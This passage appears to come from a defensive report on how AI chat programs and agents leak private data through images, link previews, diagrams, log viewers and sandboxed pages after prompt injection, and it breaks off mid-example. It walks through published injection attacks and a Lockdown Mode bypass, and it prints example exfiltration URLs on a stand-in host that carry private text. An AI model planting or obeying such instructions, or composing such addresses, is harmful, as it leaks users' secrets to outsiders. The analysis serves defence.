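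Outsiders may still have considerable influence even though developers now train models to ignore planted instructions. An injection that rarely succeeds is enough for an outsider whose page has many readers, and he may not need one at all. If his page has the best photograph of a touring bicycle, a model that follows no hidden instructions may still choose it. Training can't remove that kind of influence without making the model worse at finding pictures.

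A proxy is the usual answer to concerns about what loading an image reveals, but an ordinary proxy hides only the reader's connection and still passes on the image's address. In *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags*, on the blog of the software company Archestra, Chi (2026) proposes a stricter proxy that would contact only approved servers and would first delete everything after a question mark in the address. Chi argues that a chat program could then keep its pictures and close the leak. Deleting that part of the address isn't enough by itself, because private text can also go in the path or in a subdomain, as Microsoft (2025) points out in an account of its own defences. The protection therefore depends mostly on the list of approved servers. If the list is short, it leaves out the bicycle manufacturer's website, and the reader gets little more than provider-hosted images.

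Some chats contain very little private data that a thief could use, such as a question about bicycles from someone with a new account, no saved memories and no uploaded files. A program could reasonably load remote images automatically in such a chat and stop when the user adds a file, connects her email or mentions her health. Files and email connections are easy to detect, but a program would recognize a health problem in ordinary conversation much less reliably, so it would have to treat most long chats as private.

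The fourth premise is the easiest both to prove and to dismiss. OpenAI's check makes it impractical to send out a long conversation, which may be enough protection. But six images can still carry a login code, and an answer comparing six bicycles might well include that many. Whether the remaining leak justifies turning off images for everyone depends on how useful the images are.

### What are automatic pictures worth?

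For some questions, a picture provides most of the answer. Anthropic suggests asking Claude to show what a dish looks like before cooking it, find photos of a product, help identify a plant or insect, or compare similar items side by side. Someone choosing a campsite would probably also rather see photos of it than read a description.

Science questions need remote images less often than one might expect. Anthropic's *Visual and interactive content* describes how Claude can build a diagram or an interactive chart from scratch in the conversation. For example, a diagram can show how a derailleur moves a bicycle chain without loading a photograph from an external server.

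A generated picture can't show what a particular campsite or a bicycle for sale actually looks like. For these, the provider can show a copy that it or a search company saved earlier, so the website's owner gets no request. The search company still receives the search terms, which may be private, but that differs from sending them to an attacker. Google already runs an image search, and Anthropic uses Microsoft's, so large providers should be able to arrange this, though a small firm may have to pay for it.

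Anthropic's Claude shows recipe cards with pictures from Bing on the web and in the desktop app, while phone users get the same recipe as text. This is a limitation of the phone apps, not a security measure, but it shows that a recipe is still usable without a picture.

With placeholders, moreover, the reader doesn't lose the picture. She loses the time it takes to click, plus the occasional picture she would have liked but didn't bother to open. Call this cost *c* for each picture. Let *p* be the chance that a given picture belongs to an attack that has got past the other defences, *H* the harm if it loads, and *r* the share of such attacks that the placeholder stops, which is less than 1 because some readers will click. The off default is worthwhile if

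$$p \times r \times H > c$$

Suppose, using made-up numbers, that clicking to load an image takes two seconds of the reader's time, worth about one cent at $18 an hour, and that the placeholder stops half of the attacks. If a leak does $200 of harm, turning images off by default is worthwhile when more than one image in 10,000 is an attack. For an executive whose leak would do $200,000 of harm, the threshold is one in 10 million.

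*p* is hard to estimate because nearly all published attacks are demonstrations by researchers, so we know that leaks are possible but not how common they are. *p* also depends on the product. On a Dify or LibreChat installation with no content security policy, any successful injection can send out a long text, so both *p* and *H* are higher, and the case for turning remote images off is strong. ChatGPT's check lowers both *p* and *H*. For an ordinary reader with ordinary secrets, the benefit of automatic loading in ChatGPT may well outweigh its expected harm, and the fifth premise would then be false.

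However, averages hide the fact that everyone bears the one-cent cost while the harm falls on a few people. Most of them, like the woman who mentioned her heart condition, had no reason to expect it. A provider can also bring *c* close to zero by saving copies of common pictures, since most pictures would still appear automatically and only the rest would need a click. Provider-hosted copies, with placeholders for everything else, are probably the best default for a provider that can afford it.

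### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI lets users who expect more harm choose a stricter setting, Lockdown Mode. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it on 13 February 2026 for businesses on the Enterprise plan, universities, healthcare providers and teachers. On 4 June, OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and smaller business accounts. Willison (2026) notes in *OpenAI Help* that free accounts are included.

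The purpose is to stop the last step of an attack, in which data leaves. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the current help page, the mode has these effects:

- ChatGPT may not display images in regular answers, and doesn't retrieve images from the web. Users can still upload pictures and generate new ones.
- Web browsing uses only saved copies of pages, which may be out of date.
- Deep Research, which writes long reports from many web pages, is off, and so is Agent Mode, which carries out tasks on websites.
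- Code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing window, can't connect to the network.
- ChatGPT can't download files to analyze, though it can work on files the user uploads.

The mode doesn't change memory, so private data from earlier chats may still be in the context. Instructions planted in an uploaded file or a saved web page can also still reach the model and make its answer wrong. On personal accounts, the mode also blocks connected apps from live access to outside services where that access conflicts with its protections. In larger organizations, an administrator decides which apps remain available, and OpenAI advises against allowing any that can write data where an outsider might see it. The mode doesn't affect Codex, OpenAI's coding tool. OpenAI doesn't guarantee that the mode prevents every leak, and researchers have since published a way around it.

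OpenAI says the mode is for a small group of security-conscious users, such as executives or security teams at prominent organizations, and is "not necessary for most users". Its security chief, Dane Stuckey, also includes people who work with sensitive data. Willison likes the design because it blocks the data with fixed rules rather than relying on an AI system to judge whether a request is suspicious. But he also reads the mode's existence as an admission that ChatGPT's normal settings don't robustly protect against a determined attacker.

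That reading is fair, though the admission isn't only about images, and much of what the mode turns off, such as Agent Mode, is riskier than an image. But OpenAI says it disables some features entirely when it can't strongly guarantee data safety. If its check on public addresses gave that guarantee for images, the company would have had little reason to turn them off. This fits with the alphabet attacks, which the check makes harder but doesn't rule out.

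OpenAI can reply that no default is perfectly secure and that most people would rather have the features. This is convincing for Agent Mode but less so for images, which people could still load by clicking a placeholder. Lockdown Mode also disables Deep Research and live browsing, so someone who only wants to block external images has to give those up too. She can turn the mode off for a single chat to get them back, but images would then load automatically again.

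### Microsoft and Copilot Chat

Where possible, Microsoft prefers deterministic defences, which block a particular attack every time, to probabilistic ones, which make it less likely. It says it blocked data leaks through images deterministically after Rehberger's report, and that it looks for variants of every flaw researchers report. When it can't detect or block a risk well enough, it asks the user for consent. For example, Copilot can draft an email in Outlook, but the user has to approve and send it. Microsoft accepts that this is less convenient but considers it very effective against leaks.

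The security firm Checkmarx got a different response in October 2025. Its *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes an attack on Microsoft's Copilot Chat in which outside content made the assistant put an access key from a programmer's computer into an image address. No picture appeared in the chat, but Checkmarx's server still received the request.

Microsoft closed the report on 4 November without fixing the problem. It said the attack required several actions that users don't take by default, didn't work reliably in every environment, and involved warnings meant to reduce the risk. It also said it expects users to review and trust the code they run. But it passed the report to its engineers so they could look for ways to make the behavior clearer to users.

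These may be good reasons to give the flaw a low priority. Checkmarx concedes that getting an assistant to read the hostile material can be complicated. But Microsoft's policy, published three months earlier, was that a successful injection shouldn't lead to a leak, and here the company relied on warnings to prevent one.

It isn't clear whether Microsoft has fixed this since. Its remark about code suggests that the report concerned the version of Copilot Chat for programmers, which runs in the editor VS Code. *Secure development with AI in VS Code*, the editor's current security guide, covers permissions, passwords and network access for commands, but has no advice on images in chat answers. The editor's chat was supposed to have stopped loading remote images in May 2025. If Checkmarx tested a later version, the change may have removed the image from the screen without stopping the request.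 Developers who want to confirm that remote images are off would need to check the network traffic, because a missing image doesn't show that no request was sent.

### Do people read before they click?

In its explanation of the public index, OpenAI objects to frequent warnings mainly because they "can train people to click through prompts without thinking". Visual Studio Code's *Understand trust and safety for AI agents* describes a similar problem, approval fatigue, in which people who repeatedly approve an assistant's commands pay less attention to what they approve, especially in long sessions. Neither document gives figures, so we can't tell from them how quickly attention fades or whether it fades as much for images as for commands.

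Simple arithmetic makes the effect more plausible. Suppose a reader opens 20 placeholders a week and one in 10,000 hides an attack. On average, she'll encounter one attack every 500 weeks, or nearly ten years. All her other clicks will load harmless images, so she won't learn caution from them, and it would be unreasonable to expect her to inspect each address.

Unlike an approval prompt, an image placeholder protects users who pay no attention to it. An assistant that asks permission to run a command usually can't continue until it gets an answer, so a busy user clicks "yes" to get on with the work. A reader can ignore a placeholder because the text of the answer is already there.

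Placeholders also make the attacker's job harder. An invisible pixel becomes a visible box that nobody asked for, so the attacker needs an image the user wants to open. PromptArmor's attack on HuggingChat used hidden text to request a chart of the company's finances, which a user might well click on. Placeholders will therefore probably stop some attacks but not others, and a provider could measure the proportion by testing with harmless images.

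Fewer boxes would help. If the provider shows saved copies of most pictures automatically, the remaining boxes are unusual enough to get some attention.

### When the address is unreadable

A click can also leak data because the reader has no way to judge the address. Here is part of the bicycle example again, with the private text in base64:

```
https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=aGVhcnQtY29uZGl0aW9u
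```

The last 20 characters stand for "heart-condition". Very few people would recognize this, and the addresses of harmless photographs often contain similar strings.

The same difficulty applies to links, and Google has accepted it there. When Checkmarx reported that Gemini could still leak data through a link the user clicked, Google closed the report after four days as infeasible to fix. Gemini removes links that Google's Safe Browsing service recognizes as dangerous, but this misses new domains. A chat program can do better with images because, unlike the reader, it has a record of every page the model read. It can check whether an image's address appeared on one of those pages or was composed by the model.

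### A worked placeholder

JetBrains' message, "Image-fetching blocked for security reasons", is a poor model because it omits which image was blocked, what the danger is and what the user can do. When Menci asked the AI Assistant how to fix the problem, it began to explain browser settings, although it wasn't running in a browser. He also complains that the message appears very often when he hasn't asked for an image. A provider could prevent both problems by explaining in the model's system prompt that external images don't load automatically and why.

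OpenAI's warning for unverified links is better because it names the danger. OpenAI also shows the address and lets users copy or open the link, but they have to check it themselves.

A placeholder for pictures could give her more to go on:

```
Picture not loaded
Description from the assistant: "Green touring bicycle"
Server: bikes.example (not run by this chat service)
Address: copied from a page the assistant read [view page]
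Loading it sends this address and your IP address to bikes.example.
[Load once]   [Show full address]
```

From this, the reader can tell whether she wants the picture, whether she recognizes the server, and whether the picture plausibly belongs to the page it came from. She also learns that the server will receive her IP address. Hidden text can influence the description, so the program should label it as the assistant's. The program should write all the other lines itself.

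If an image's address isn't on any page the model read, the program should leave out the "Load once" button. The model may have added private text to the address, and the reader can't tell whether it has. Readers lose little without the button, since an address the model made up often won't work. The pixel whose address contains the heart condition would never load, even if its description made the reader want to see it.

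The box can't protect the reader from every leak. With the 365 dated pictures of bicycles, the program would correctly report that both addresses came from a page the model had read. She might wonder why an answer about bicycles needs these two pictures, but she couldn't learn from the box that the choice of pictures gives away her travel dates.

The program should load one picture per click. A "Load all" button would be convenient for comparing six bicycles, but one click could also send a six-digit login code to a server, with one digit in each picture request. A button to trust a server permanently would create a similar risk, because the model could later use pictures from that server to send it a secret without another click.

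The program must also draw the box without contacting the server. Fetching a small preview, the website's icon or even the picture's dimensions would send the request the box is meant to prevent.

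## Link previews, diagrams and live pages in a chat

Chat programs, like the mail programs in the Efail tests, have several features besides remote images that can contact an outside server without any action by the reader. A setting meant to prevent automatic loading has to cover them all. Some send the request from the reader's browser, and others send it from a computer that her settings don't affect.

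### Link previews

When someone posts a link in Slack, Discord or Telegram, the app usually fetches the linked page to show its title and a small picture. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, relays Rehberger's warning that these previews can leak private text when a chatbot is in the conversation. If hidden text makes the bot post a link with private text in its address, the app sends that text to the link's owner when it fetches the page.

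Suppose the woman who asked about touring bicycles uses an assistant through Telegram. Its summary of the review ends with an ordinary link to more photographs:

```
https://pictures.example/more?note=heart-condition_house-empty-3-to-24-June
```

In a chat program without link previews, nothing would leak unless the user clicked the link. Telegram fetches the linked page to build a preview as soon as the assistant posts its answer, possibly before the user has read it.

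In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reported that OpenClaw had this problem under its default Telegram settings. PromptArmor built a website where people can test their own agents. In its demonstration, the site's log recorded a name and an access key from a preview request. OpenClaw's own control page loads almost no outside images, but that doesn't protect someone who reads the answers in Telegram, because Telegram's rules apply there.

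Slack's and Telegram's preview services are among the programs that fetch pages from the test site. Because the messaging company makes the request, the link's owner doesn't see the reader's IP address but still receives everything in the link, as with Gmail's image proxy.

Both products have a way to turn previews off. A developer whose bot posts to Slack can add two settings to each message, and an OpenClaw user can add one line to a configuration file. But previews stay on until someone learns about the problem and changes the settings, and in Slack only the bot's developer can do that. PromptArmor would like messaging companies to offer the choice for each channel. It would be simpler to turn previews off by default for links that bots post. The messaging company knows which accounts are bots, and readers could still open the links.

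### Pictures inside diagrams

Many chat programs can draw a diagram from a short text description. Mermaid, a popular notation for this, lets the author put a picture in one of the boxes. In schematic form, a model might write:

```
diagram: Reader --> Shop
picture in the "Shop" box: https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=(private text)
```

An output filter that searches for Markdown image code won't find images loaded through a Mermaid diagram. *Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) examined eight coding agents, which are assistants that can read files and run commands on a programmer's computer. In one agent, which the paper doesn't name, the Mermaid renderer fetched such images.

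Lee and colleagues used the flaw in a longer attack. They planted instructions in an issue, a kind of bug report attached to a software project, and had the agent fetch it. The agent then opened a settings file outside the project, copied an access key from it and wrote a diagram with the key in a picture's address. The user didn't have to approve any of these steps. The vendor already knew about the flaw when they reported it, and has since patched it.

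Coding agents often ask for approval before they do something risky. Of the agents with a built-in tool for fetching web pages, Lee and colleagues found only one that didn't ask first. Nobody had thought of drawing a diagram as fetching a web page, so diagrams were rendered without an approval prompt. Some vendors rejected other findings from the study as intended behavior.

In a browser, an image allowlist in the content security policy would also stop this leak, but a desktop program that draws diagrams by other means needs its own check.

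### Answers that someone else opens later

Chat programs store answers, and other people may open them in another program, such as OpenAI's log viewer, which loaded images. The demonstration in PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* uses a mock tool that helps a bank check its customers' identities. One of the tool's six sources contained hidden instructions, and the model produced code for an image with the customer's details in its address. A second model, which checked each answer before it was displayed, recognized the attack and blocked it.

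The block also flagged the conversation for review, which led the developer to open it in the log viewer, the only place where the attack still worked. The attacker then received the customer's passport and financial details.

An application that removes image codes or shows only plain text has the same problem. PromptArmor shows an answer from the search assistant Perplexity that was odd and nearly empty after the software stripped out an image. A user might well click "thumbs down" on such an answer, and a developer might then open the log. PromptArmor also found insecure images in five other OpenAI tools for developers, including the previews where developers test an application while building it.

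PromptArmor submitted the report on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that screens such reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd closed it as "not applicable" on 4 December, before OpenAI had seen it. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI confirmed the flaw, reopened the report on 22 January 2026 and said a fix was underway.

A log viewer has little need to display pictures. A developer investigating a strange answer needs the exact text the model wrote, including any image code, and plain text shows that better than a formatted page.

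### Requests from the agent's tools

An agent can also send data without putting anything in its answer. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, measured how often this happened in a test system. When the user mentions a web address, their agent automatically fetches the page and adds its title, description and text to the model's context. They call this a "preview", though the word means something different in Telegram. The data leaves after this step, through a tool that lets the agent make web requests.

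They ran a small open model, qwen2.5:7b, on their own computers and placed a made-up secret in its context. The user always asked the model to summarize a page that contained a fake system instruction to "verify connectivity" by requesting an address that included the secret. They tried four positions for the instruction, with and without redirects, and told the model to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

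At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88 percent, though the abstract gives about 89). In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the answer on screen was harmless, so a safety check of the answer alone would have missed them. The attacks used no images, so turning off images would not have stopped them.

The setup favored the attacker, as Lan and colleagues acknowledge. The model was small and had almost no safety instructions, and the secret was in plain view. The attack was also obvious, and GPT-4o resisted obvious orders in all 200 of Rahman and Kim's trials, so the 88 percent figure is a poor guide to how often a current product would fail. Lan and colleagues suspect that stronger models may do worse because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. That is possible for well-disguised attacks, but Lan and colleagues tested only one model.

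Their results for split secrets are also hard to interpret. The attack worked in 238 of 240 runs when the model had to send one request, and in 185 of 240 when it had to send four. The share of runs with sensitive data in the first request fell from 97 to 26 percent, which they present as evidence that splitting helps an attacker avoid detection. But their measure counts any piece of the secret, so a low figure may just mean that the model often sent the wrong thing. They report 16 percent for the first three requests together, but by their own definition this can't be lower than the figure for the first request alone. They don't report how often all four pieces arrived.

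The comparison of defences is more useful, although it used only the easiest version of the attack, with 30 runs for each defence:

| Defence | Runs in which the agent contacted the attacker |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Tags that mark the page as untrusted | 100% |
| A rule against following instructions from the web | 67% |
| Both | 57% |
| An allowlist for the request tool | 0% |

With the allowlist in place, the agent still tried to send the secret in every run, and the tool blocked each attempt. Filters for suspicious addresses also stopped every attack, but one of them searched for words such as "collect", which was in the attack's address and which a real attacker would avoid.

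Data can also leak through code that runs on the provider's computers. ChatGPT can write and run programs in an isolated environment, for example to analyze a spreadsheet. According to Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026), this environment had a hidden path to the public internet, and one malicious prompt was enough to send the user's messages and uploaded files out through it.

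### Live pages in sandboxed frames

Some chat programs let the model write a small working web page, such as a gear ratio calculator, and display it in the conversation. Such a page needs scripts, which can do much more than an image tag, so chat programs put it in a sandboxed frame. The browser isolates the frame from the rest of the chat page and restricts what its contents can do.

The frame has a different origin (roughly, a different web address) from the chat page. Browsers don't let a page from one origin read a page from another, so a script in the frame can't read the conversation around it or use the reader's login. The chat program also marks the frame as sandboxed, which under the HTML standard turns off scripts, forms, popup windows and several other abilities. The program then turns back on the ones the framed page needs.

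Neither measure stops the frame from contacting other servers, for example to request a picture, and the page may already contain private text. A model that follows hidden instructions could write the calculator's code so that it requests a picture from an address containing the reader's heart condition. So the frame also needs a content security policy that blocks requests to outside servers. If a page has a good reason to contact one, such as to get current bicycle prices, the chat program can ask the reader for permission. OpenAI says ChatGPT's Canvas and Apps features run in a sandbox that detects unexpected communications and asks the user for consent.

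The separate origin mainly protects the reader's account and other chats, while the network rules protect whatever is inside the frame. A chat program needs both, and in 2026 researchers found a way to bypass each in ChatGPT.

### MCP Apps and the Apps SDK

Companies can also supply live pages for a chat. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting chat programs to outside tools and data. These tools could originally return only text and structured data, but an extension called MCP Apps lets them return interactive pages, such as maps or charts. People from OpenAI, Anthropic and an earlier project called MCP-UI wrote the extension's specification, *SEP-1865* (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025), which has had stable status since 26 January 2026.

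The Model Context Protocol (2025) announcement describes several safeguards. Every app's page runs in a sandboxed frame with restricted permissions. The company supplies the page's template in advance, separately from its data, so the chat program can inspect the template before showing it. Messages between the frame and the chat program use a format that the program can log. The chat program can also require the reader's approval before a page uses a tool, but this is optional.

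By default, an app may not contact any server. According to Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS*, an app's maker must declare every outside server in advance, with one list for data connections and another for scripts, styles, fonts and images. Model Context Protocol's *Interface McpUiResourceCsp* adds lists for other frames inside the page and for the base address used to complete relative links. The chat program turns these lists into a content security policy. Claude can also give each app its own web address, calculated from the address of the company's server, so apps from different companies have different origins.

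These lists protect the reader if hostile text gets into an app's data. For example, a map app might display customer reviews, one of which contains an image tag that points to `pictures.example`. If the app's maker didn't declare that server, the browser blocks the request.

They don't protect her from the app's maker, who writes the lists. The maker can include its own server, and pictures from there will then load automatically, whatever the reader has chosen for images in ordinary answers. mcp-use's *Content Security Policy*, the documentation for a toolkit that many kinds of MCP app can use, explains that the toolkit adds the app's own server to the lists once the developer has entered its address. This is reasonable because an app has to get its scripts from somewhere, but it means that an app can often send information back to the company that made it.

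The Apps SDK is OpenAI's kit for building apps inside ChatGPT. It is based on MCP and was one of the models for MCP Apps, so the two systems isolate apps in much the same way. An app's page runs in a sandboxed frame, and the developer must explicitly allow each outside server. The SDK's main addition is that OpenAI asks for consent to unexpected communications. In both systems, the frame isolates only the part of an app that the reader sees. The tool behind it runs on the app maker's server and receives whatever the model sends.

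The chat program could paste the app's HTML directly into a frame, without a separate web address. According to a talk at AI Engineer (2026), a developer conference, such a frame inherits the chat page's environment, which was never meant for an outside company's code. MCP and ChatGPT apps avoid this by using two nested frames.

### The account takeover

In October 2026, researchers at the security firm Parameter got a frame of that kind into ChatGPT, starting with Preview, a feature that displays HTML from an answer as a working page. In *Do the Math*, Goyal (2026) describes how an attacker could have used it to take over the account of anyone who opened a shared conversation.

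The Preview frame was on a separate address, and code inside it couldn't read the chat page. But browsers let frames send each other messages, and the receiving page is responsible for checking who sent them. The shared conversation also contained an interactive graph. To draw it, ChatGPT loaded a math library into the main page. The library accepted messages about its on-screen keyboard from any sender, and these messages could contain HTML.

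The Preview sent one, and the library inserted the researchers' HTML into the main page. The HTML created a frame with no sandbox, which the browser treated as part of chatgpt.com. ChatGPT's content security policy still blocked scripts written directly into the page, but it allowed scripts from YouTube, and the researchers found a way to make YouTube return a script of their own. This is the same weakness that let data out through Teams and Bing, except that here the approved server was used to load an attacker's code.

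The script then had the same access as the signed-in user. It listed her conversations, opened a private one and sent part of it to the researchers. According to Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, the script sent the data in the address of an image. OpenAI's check on image addresses presumably didn't apply, because the script could request the image itself instead of having ChatGPT display one.

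The graph and the Preview were each harmless alone, so a security review that tested them separately could easily have passed both. One early version of the attack put the HTML in an attachment, but it failed because ChatGPT left the graph out of the shared copy.

In the most reliable version of the attack, the victim clicked the Preview button once, while in a later version the Preview opened by itself. Parameter reported the flaw on 18 October. OpenAI gave it the highest severity rating, fixed it eight days later and paid $5,000, which Willison thought a bit cheap. The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026) notes that Parameter reported no real attacks, and that blocking YouTube alone wouldn't have been enough, since the Preview could still have put HTML into the main page.

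### The way around Lockdown Mode

The security firm Check Point found a different flaw in the same feature. It affected even people who had turned on Lockdown Mode, which blocks images in answers to prevent data leaks. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) gives Check Point's explanation.

The Preview's sandbox allowed popup windows and let them escape the sandbox. ChatGPT tried to prevent misuse by intercepting the browser function that opens windows, but a page in the Preview could create another frame inside itself and use that frame's unmodified copy of the function. The resulting window was free of the sandbox's restrictions and could send data to an attacker's server. In the desktop app, this could happen without a click. The attacker also controlled what the window displayed and could have shown a fake ChatGPT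 update containing malware.

An attacker could deliver the page through a crafted prompt, a shared chat or a malicious GPT (a customized version of ChatGPT that anyone can publish). OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026, and the details became public on 5 November.

ChatGPT relied on a check that ran in the same place as the code it was supposed to restrain. Under the HTML standard, a chat program can instead withhold permission for popups, and the browser then refuses to open one no matter which copy of the function the page calls. A content security policy wouldn't have been a good substitute because it governs what a page loads into itself and has little control over new windows.

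### A default that covers every request

No single control reaches all of these features, because the requests come from different people's computers:

| Feature | Whose computer sends the request | What would stop it |
|---|---|---|
| Diagram with a remote picture | The reader's | The page's content security policy |
| Live page | The reader's | A policy for the frame, and no permission for popups |
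| Link preview | Usually the messaging company's | Previews off for messages from bots |
| Stored answer | The developer's | Plain text in the log viewer |
| Web request tool | The agent's or the provider's | An allowlist for the tool |

A provider can still give readers one setting that controls every feature. Lockdown Mode works largely by turning off a list of risky features, so it protects readers only if that list is complete. It left HTML previews available, and Check Point used them to get around the restrictions. With this design, if a developer adds a new feature, such as a second kind of diagram, its pictures load by default, and the problem goes unnoticed until a researcher finds it. A safer design blocks all outside requests except those on an approved list, so the new feature's pictures don't load unless the developer asks for an exception.

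Such a setting would make some answers plainer, but perhaps not much less useful. According to Model Context Protocol, a tool that uses MCP Apps returns text if the chat program doesn't support interactive pages. A reader who turned apps off would get, for example, a list of bicycle shops instead of a map.

The provider can't apply its setting in Telegram or in another company's log viewer. But it can check each address before sending the text, as with the image placeholder, and either remove any address the model seems to have composed or break it up so that no program treats it as a link. This would occasionally spoil a useful link that the model had remembered correctly, but it would have stopped the leaks through Telegram and the log viewer.

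Providers can test this fairly easily. They can set up a server with an address that nobody else knows, have the model put that address in an image, a link, a diagram and a live page, and open the answer everywhere it might appear: on the website, in the phone and desktop apps, in Slack, in the logs. Any request to the server reveals a feature the setting doesn't cover. Detecting attacks on a working product is harder, because a monitor must pick out one strange server among the thousands that agents contact for good reasons. Lan and colleagues argue that outgoing requests are a reliable sign of an attack, because their agent never contacted the attacker's server in 120 runs with harmless pages. But those pages didn't contain the server's address, so the agent had no way to contact it.

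## Which parts of an answer come from the model

A chat program can control every request and still leave the reader unsure whose words and pictures she is looking at. The obvious labels are "AI-generated" and "external", but many parts of an answer fit neither. Suppose the summary of the bicycle review looks like this:

```
For a first tour, comfort matters more than weight.
The reviewer calls the frame "heavy but nearly indestructible".
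Northside Cycles is the best place to buy it.
[photograph of a green bicycle]
```

The model composed the opening sentence and copied the quoted words from the review. It wrote the sentence about Northside Cycles because hidden text under the review contained an instruction to recommend that shop. The photograph came from another server when the answer appeared. In this report, these four kinds of content are called composed, copied, directed and loaded.

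Directed text, in which a model writes the words but an outsider chooses the message, is the hardest to label. A model generated the sentence about Northside Cycles, but labeling it "AI-generated" would lend the assistant's credibility to an advertisement. "External" is also wrong, because the sentence may not exist anywhere outside the answer.

Text like this is easy to produce. In *Prompt-in-Content Attacks*, Lian, Wang and colleagues (2025) put a single instruction in the middle of a Word document, uploaded it to seven chat services and asked for a summary. They tried four instructions: refuse the task, output an unrelated sentence, send the reader to a website, or describe the document as outdated and mostly useless. Grok 3, DeepSeek R1 and Kimi followed all four, while ChatGPT and Claude followed none. The instruction to describe the document as outdated worked on five of the seven services,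 more than any other. Readers are also least likely to notice it, because the result still looks like a summary. These counts are only a rough guide, because Kimi's responses varied between identical tests and all the models date from 2025 or earlier.

### What the chat program can find out

| Content | What the program can know | What it can't know |
|---|---|---|
| Loaded | Which server it came from, and when | Who made it, or whether it's accurate |
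| Copied | Whether the same words are in a source the model read | Whether the source is right |
| Composed | Everything the model had in its context | Which parts of the context influenced a given sentence |
| Directed | Whether the answer changes without a particular source | Whether the model obeyed an instruction or weighed evidence |

Loaded content is the easiest to identify because the chat page itself makes the request. (A link preview in Telegram is an exception, since the messaging company fetches it.)

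To detect copying, the program can check whether the answer shares any run of, for example, eight words with the source text. This finds quotations but misses paraphrases and translations. Software can also compare passages by meaning, but *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) warns that similarity scores fail on short or restructured text. Something as short as a price or a date may be the most important part of the answer. The program also doesn't have the model's training data, so a sentence that seems to be the model's own could be quoted from that data.

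No comparison can identify directed text. A model might recommend Northside Cycles because hidden text contained an instruction to do so, or because the reviewer liked the shop. The wording could be the same in both cases, and then it would not show which one happened.

The provider can get more evidence by running the model again without the review. If the recommendation disappears, the review influenced it, but removing an honest review would have the same effect. Removing one sentence of the review at a time is more informative because it might show that the recommendation depends on a line of white text on a white background, although each test requires another run of the model.

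*Sightline* (2026) compares ways of estimating which inputs influenced an agent's tool calls. With two small models as agents, its best method scored 93.2 and 83.5 at separating calls that carried out a planted instruction from other calls (50 is chance, 100 is perfect). Sentences in a summary would probably be harder to judge, because a summary is supposed to reflect the page and the page's influence isn't suspicious in itself.

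### Five hard cases

A link in a summary can combine copied and generated text. The model may have copied the address from a review, written the clickable words ("official shop") itself, and included the link only because of an instruction in hidden text. The program can search for the address in the pages the model read, but there may be no source to check for the word "official".

The model usually makes a chart by writing code, which ordinary software runs to draw it, so the model may never receive the finished image. The key fact is where the numbers came from. If the code read them from a spreadsheet, the program can identify which one, because it ran the code. If the model typed them into the code, they could be copied from a web page, recalled from training or made up. The program can search the sources for them, but a number like 12 appears on so many pages that a match is weak evidence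 of where it came from.

A photograph from a search engine, like those Claude gets from Bing, is loaded content, but it still had to be selected and the text beside it written. The program has the picture's address and that of the page it came from, but no information about who took the photograph or whether it shows the object described in the text, such as a bicycle.

Pictures can also change. Suppose a model that can view images looks at the green bicycle and writes that it has a rear rack. Before the reader opens the answer, the server's owner replaces the file with a picture of a racing bicycle. The model's sentence is accurate about the original picture, but the reader sees the new one. The provider could keep a fingerprint of the original file, a short code computed from its contents, and compare it with the new file's. To do this, it would have to fetch the new file through its own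 server, since a chat page normally can't read the contents of an image from another site. Websites also resize and recompress their pictures, which changes the fingerprint but not what the picture shows. It would be simpler to save the file the model saw and show that.

Some chat programs display a reasoning trace, the notes a model writes before it answers. A trace might contain the sentence "The page says to recommend Northside Cycles, but she didn't ask for a shop." The model composed this sentence, but part of it repeats the attacker's text. Quotation marks don't prove that words came from the page, because the model can put them around words that aren't there. The trace can also leak data if the model quotes an image code while deciding not to use it, because a renderer that formats the trace will still load the image.

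### How a web page loses its origins

In *What It Is, Not What It Says*, Iqbal (2026) describes how AI agents lose the browser's separation between origins. The agents receive a page as a screenshot or plain text, so a third-party advertisement arrives in the same form as the site's own checkout button, and the model cannot reliably tell them apart.

Software could try to record who wrote each part of the page before the model reads it. The browser's own records aren't good enough for this. In September 2026, Iqbal loaded 1,270 websites and tracked which script created or changed each element (a paragraph, a button and so on). On an average page, Iqbal's method attributed 22.7 percent of the elements to third parties, while the browser attributed 10 percent. When a third party's script writes an element directly into the site's page, the browser treats it as the site's own. Across all the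 pages, the browser missed 58.7 percent of third-party elements this way.

If a sentence in the answer matched a line on `bikes.example`, these records could show that an advertiser's script had put the line there. They wouldn't expose a hostile reader comment that the site stores and serves itself, because Iqbal's method treats everything from the site's own server as trusted.

Iqbal also built an agent, INTACT, that keeps the elements separate while the model plans what to click or type. The model receives one element at a time and can act only on that one, and INTACT needs the user's permission before it interacts with anything from a third party. Iqbal planted attacks on 1,091 of the pages and instructed the model to follow them, to test what happens when an agent is completely fooled. A conventional agent, which read the whole page at once, followed the attack on 73.1 percent of the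 pages. With INTACT, 12.8 percent of attacks got through the planning stage, and each of those could at most produce a request for the user's permission.

INTACT takes a median of 83 seconds to plan a task, compared with 2.5 for the conventional agent. Iqbal estimates that isolation reduces functionality on 3.7 percent of tasks, those where an AI judge accepted only the conventional agent's plan. The true figure may be higher, since the judge couldn't decide on about a third of the plans and nobody carried them out. It would certainly be higher for summaries, because INTACT's planner can't compare values in different elements. For example, it couldn't identify which of two bicycles has the lower gear.

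### When Markdown marks the boundary

The model could mark the origins itself by putting everything it quotes in a box. The usual box in Markdown is a fenced block, which starts and ends with a line of at least three backticks. The start can also name a language, but otherwise the two lines look the same, and this causes trouble when the quoted text has a fenced block of its own. With FENCE standing for three backticks:

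```
FENCE markdown      opens the box
Some quoted text
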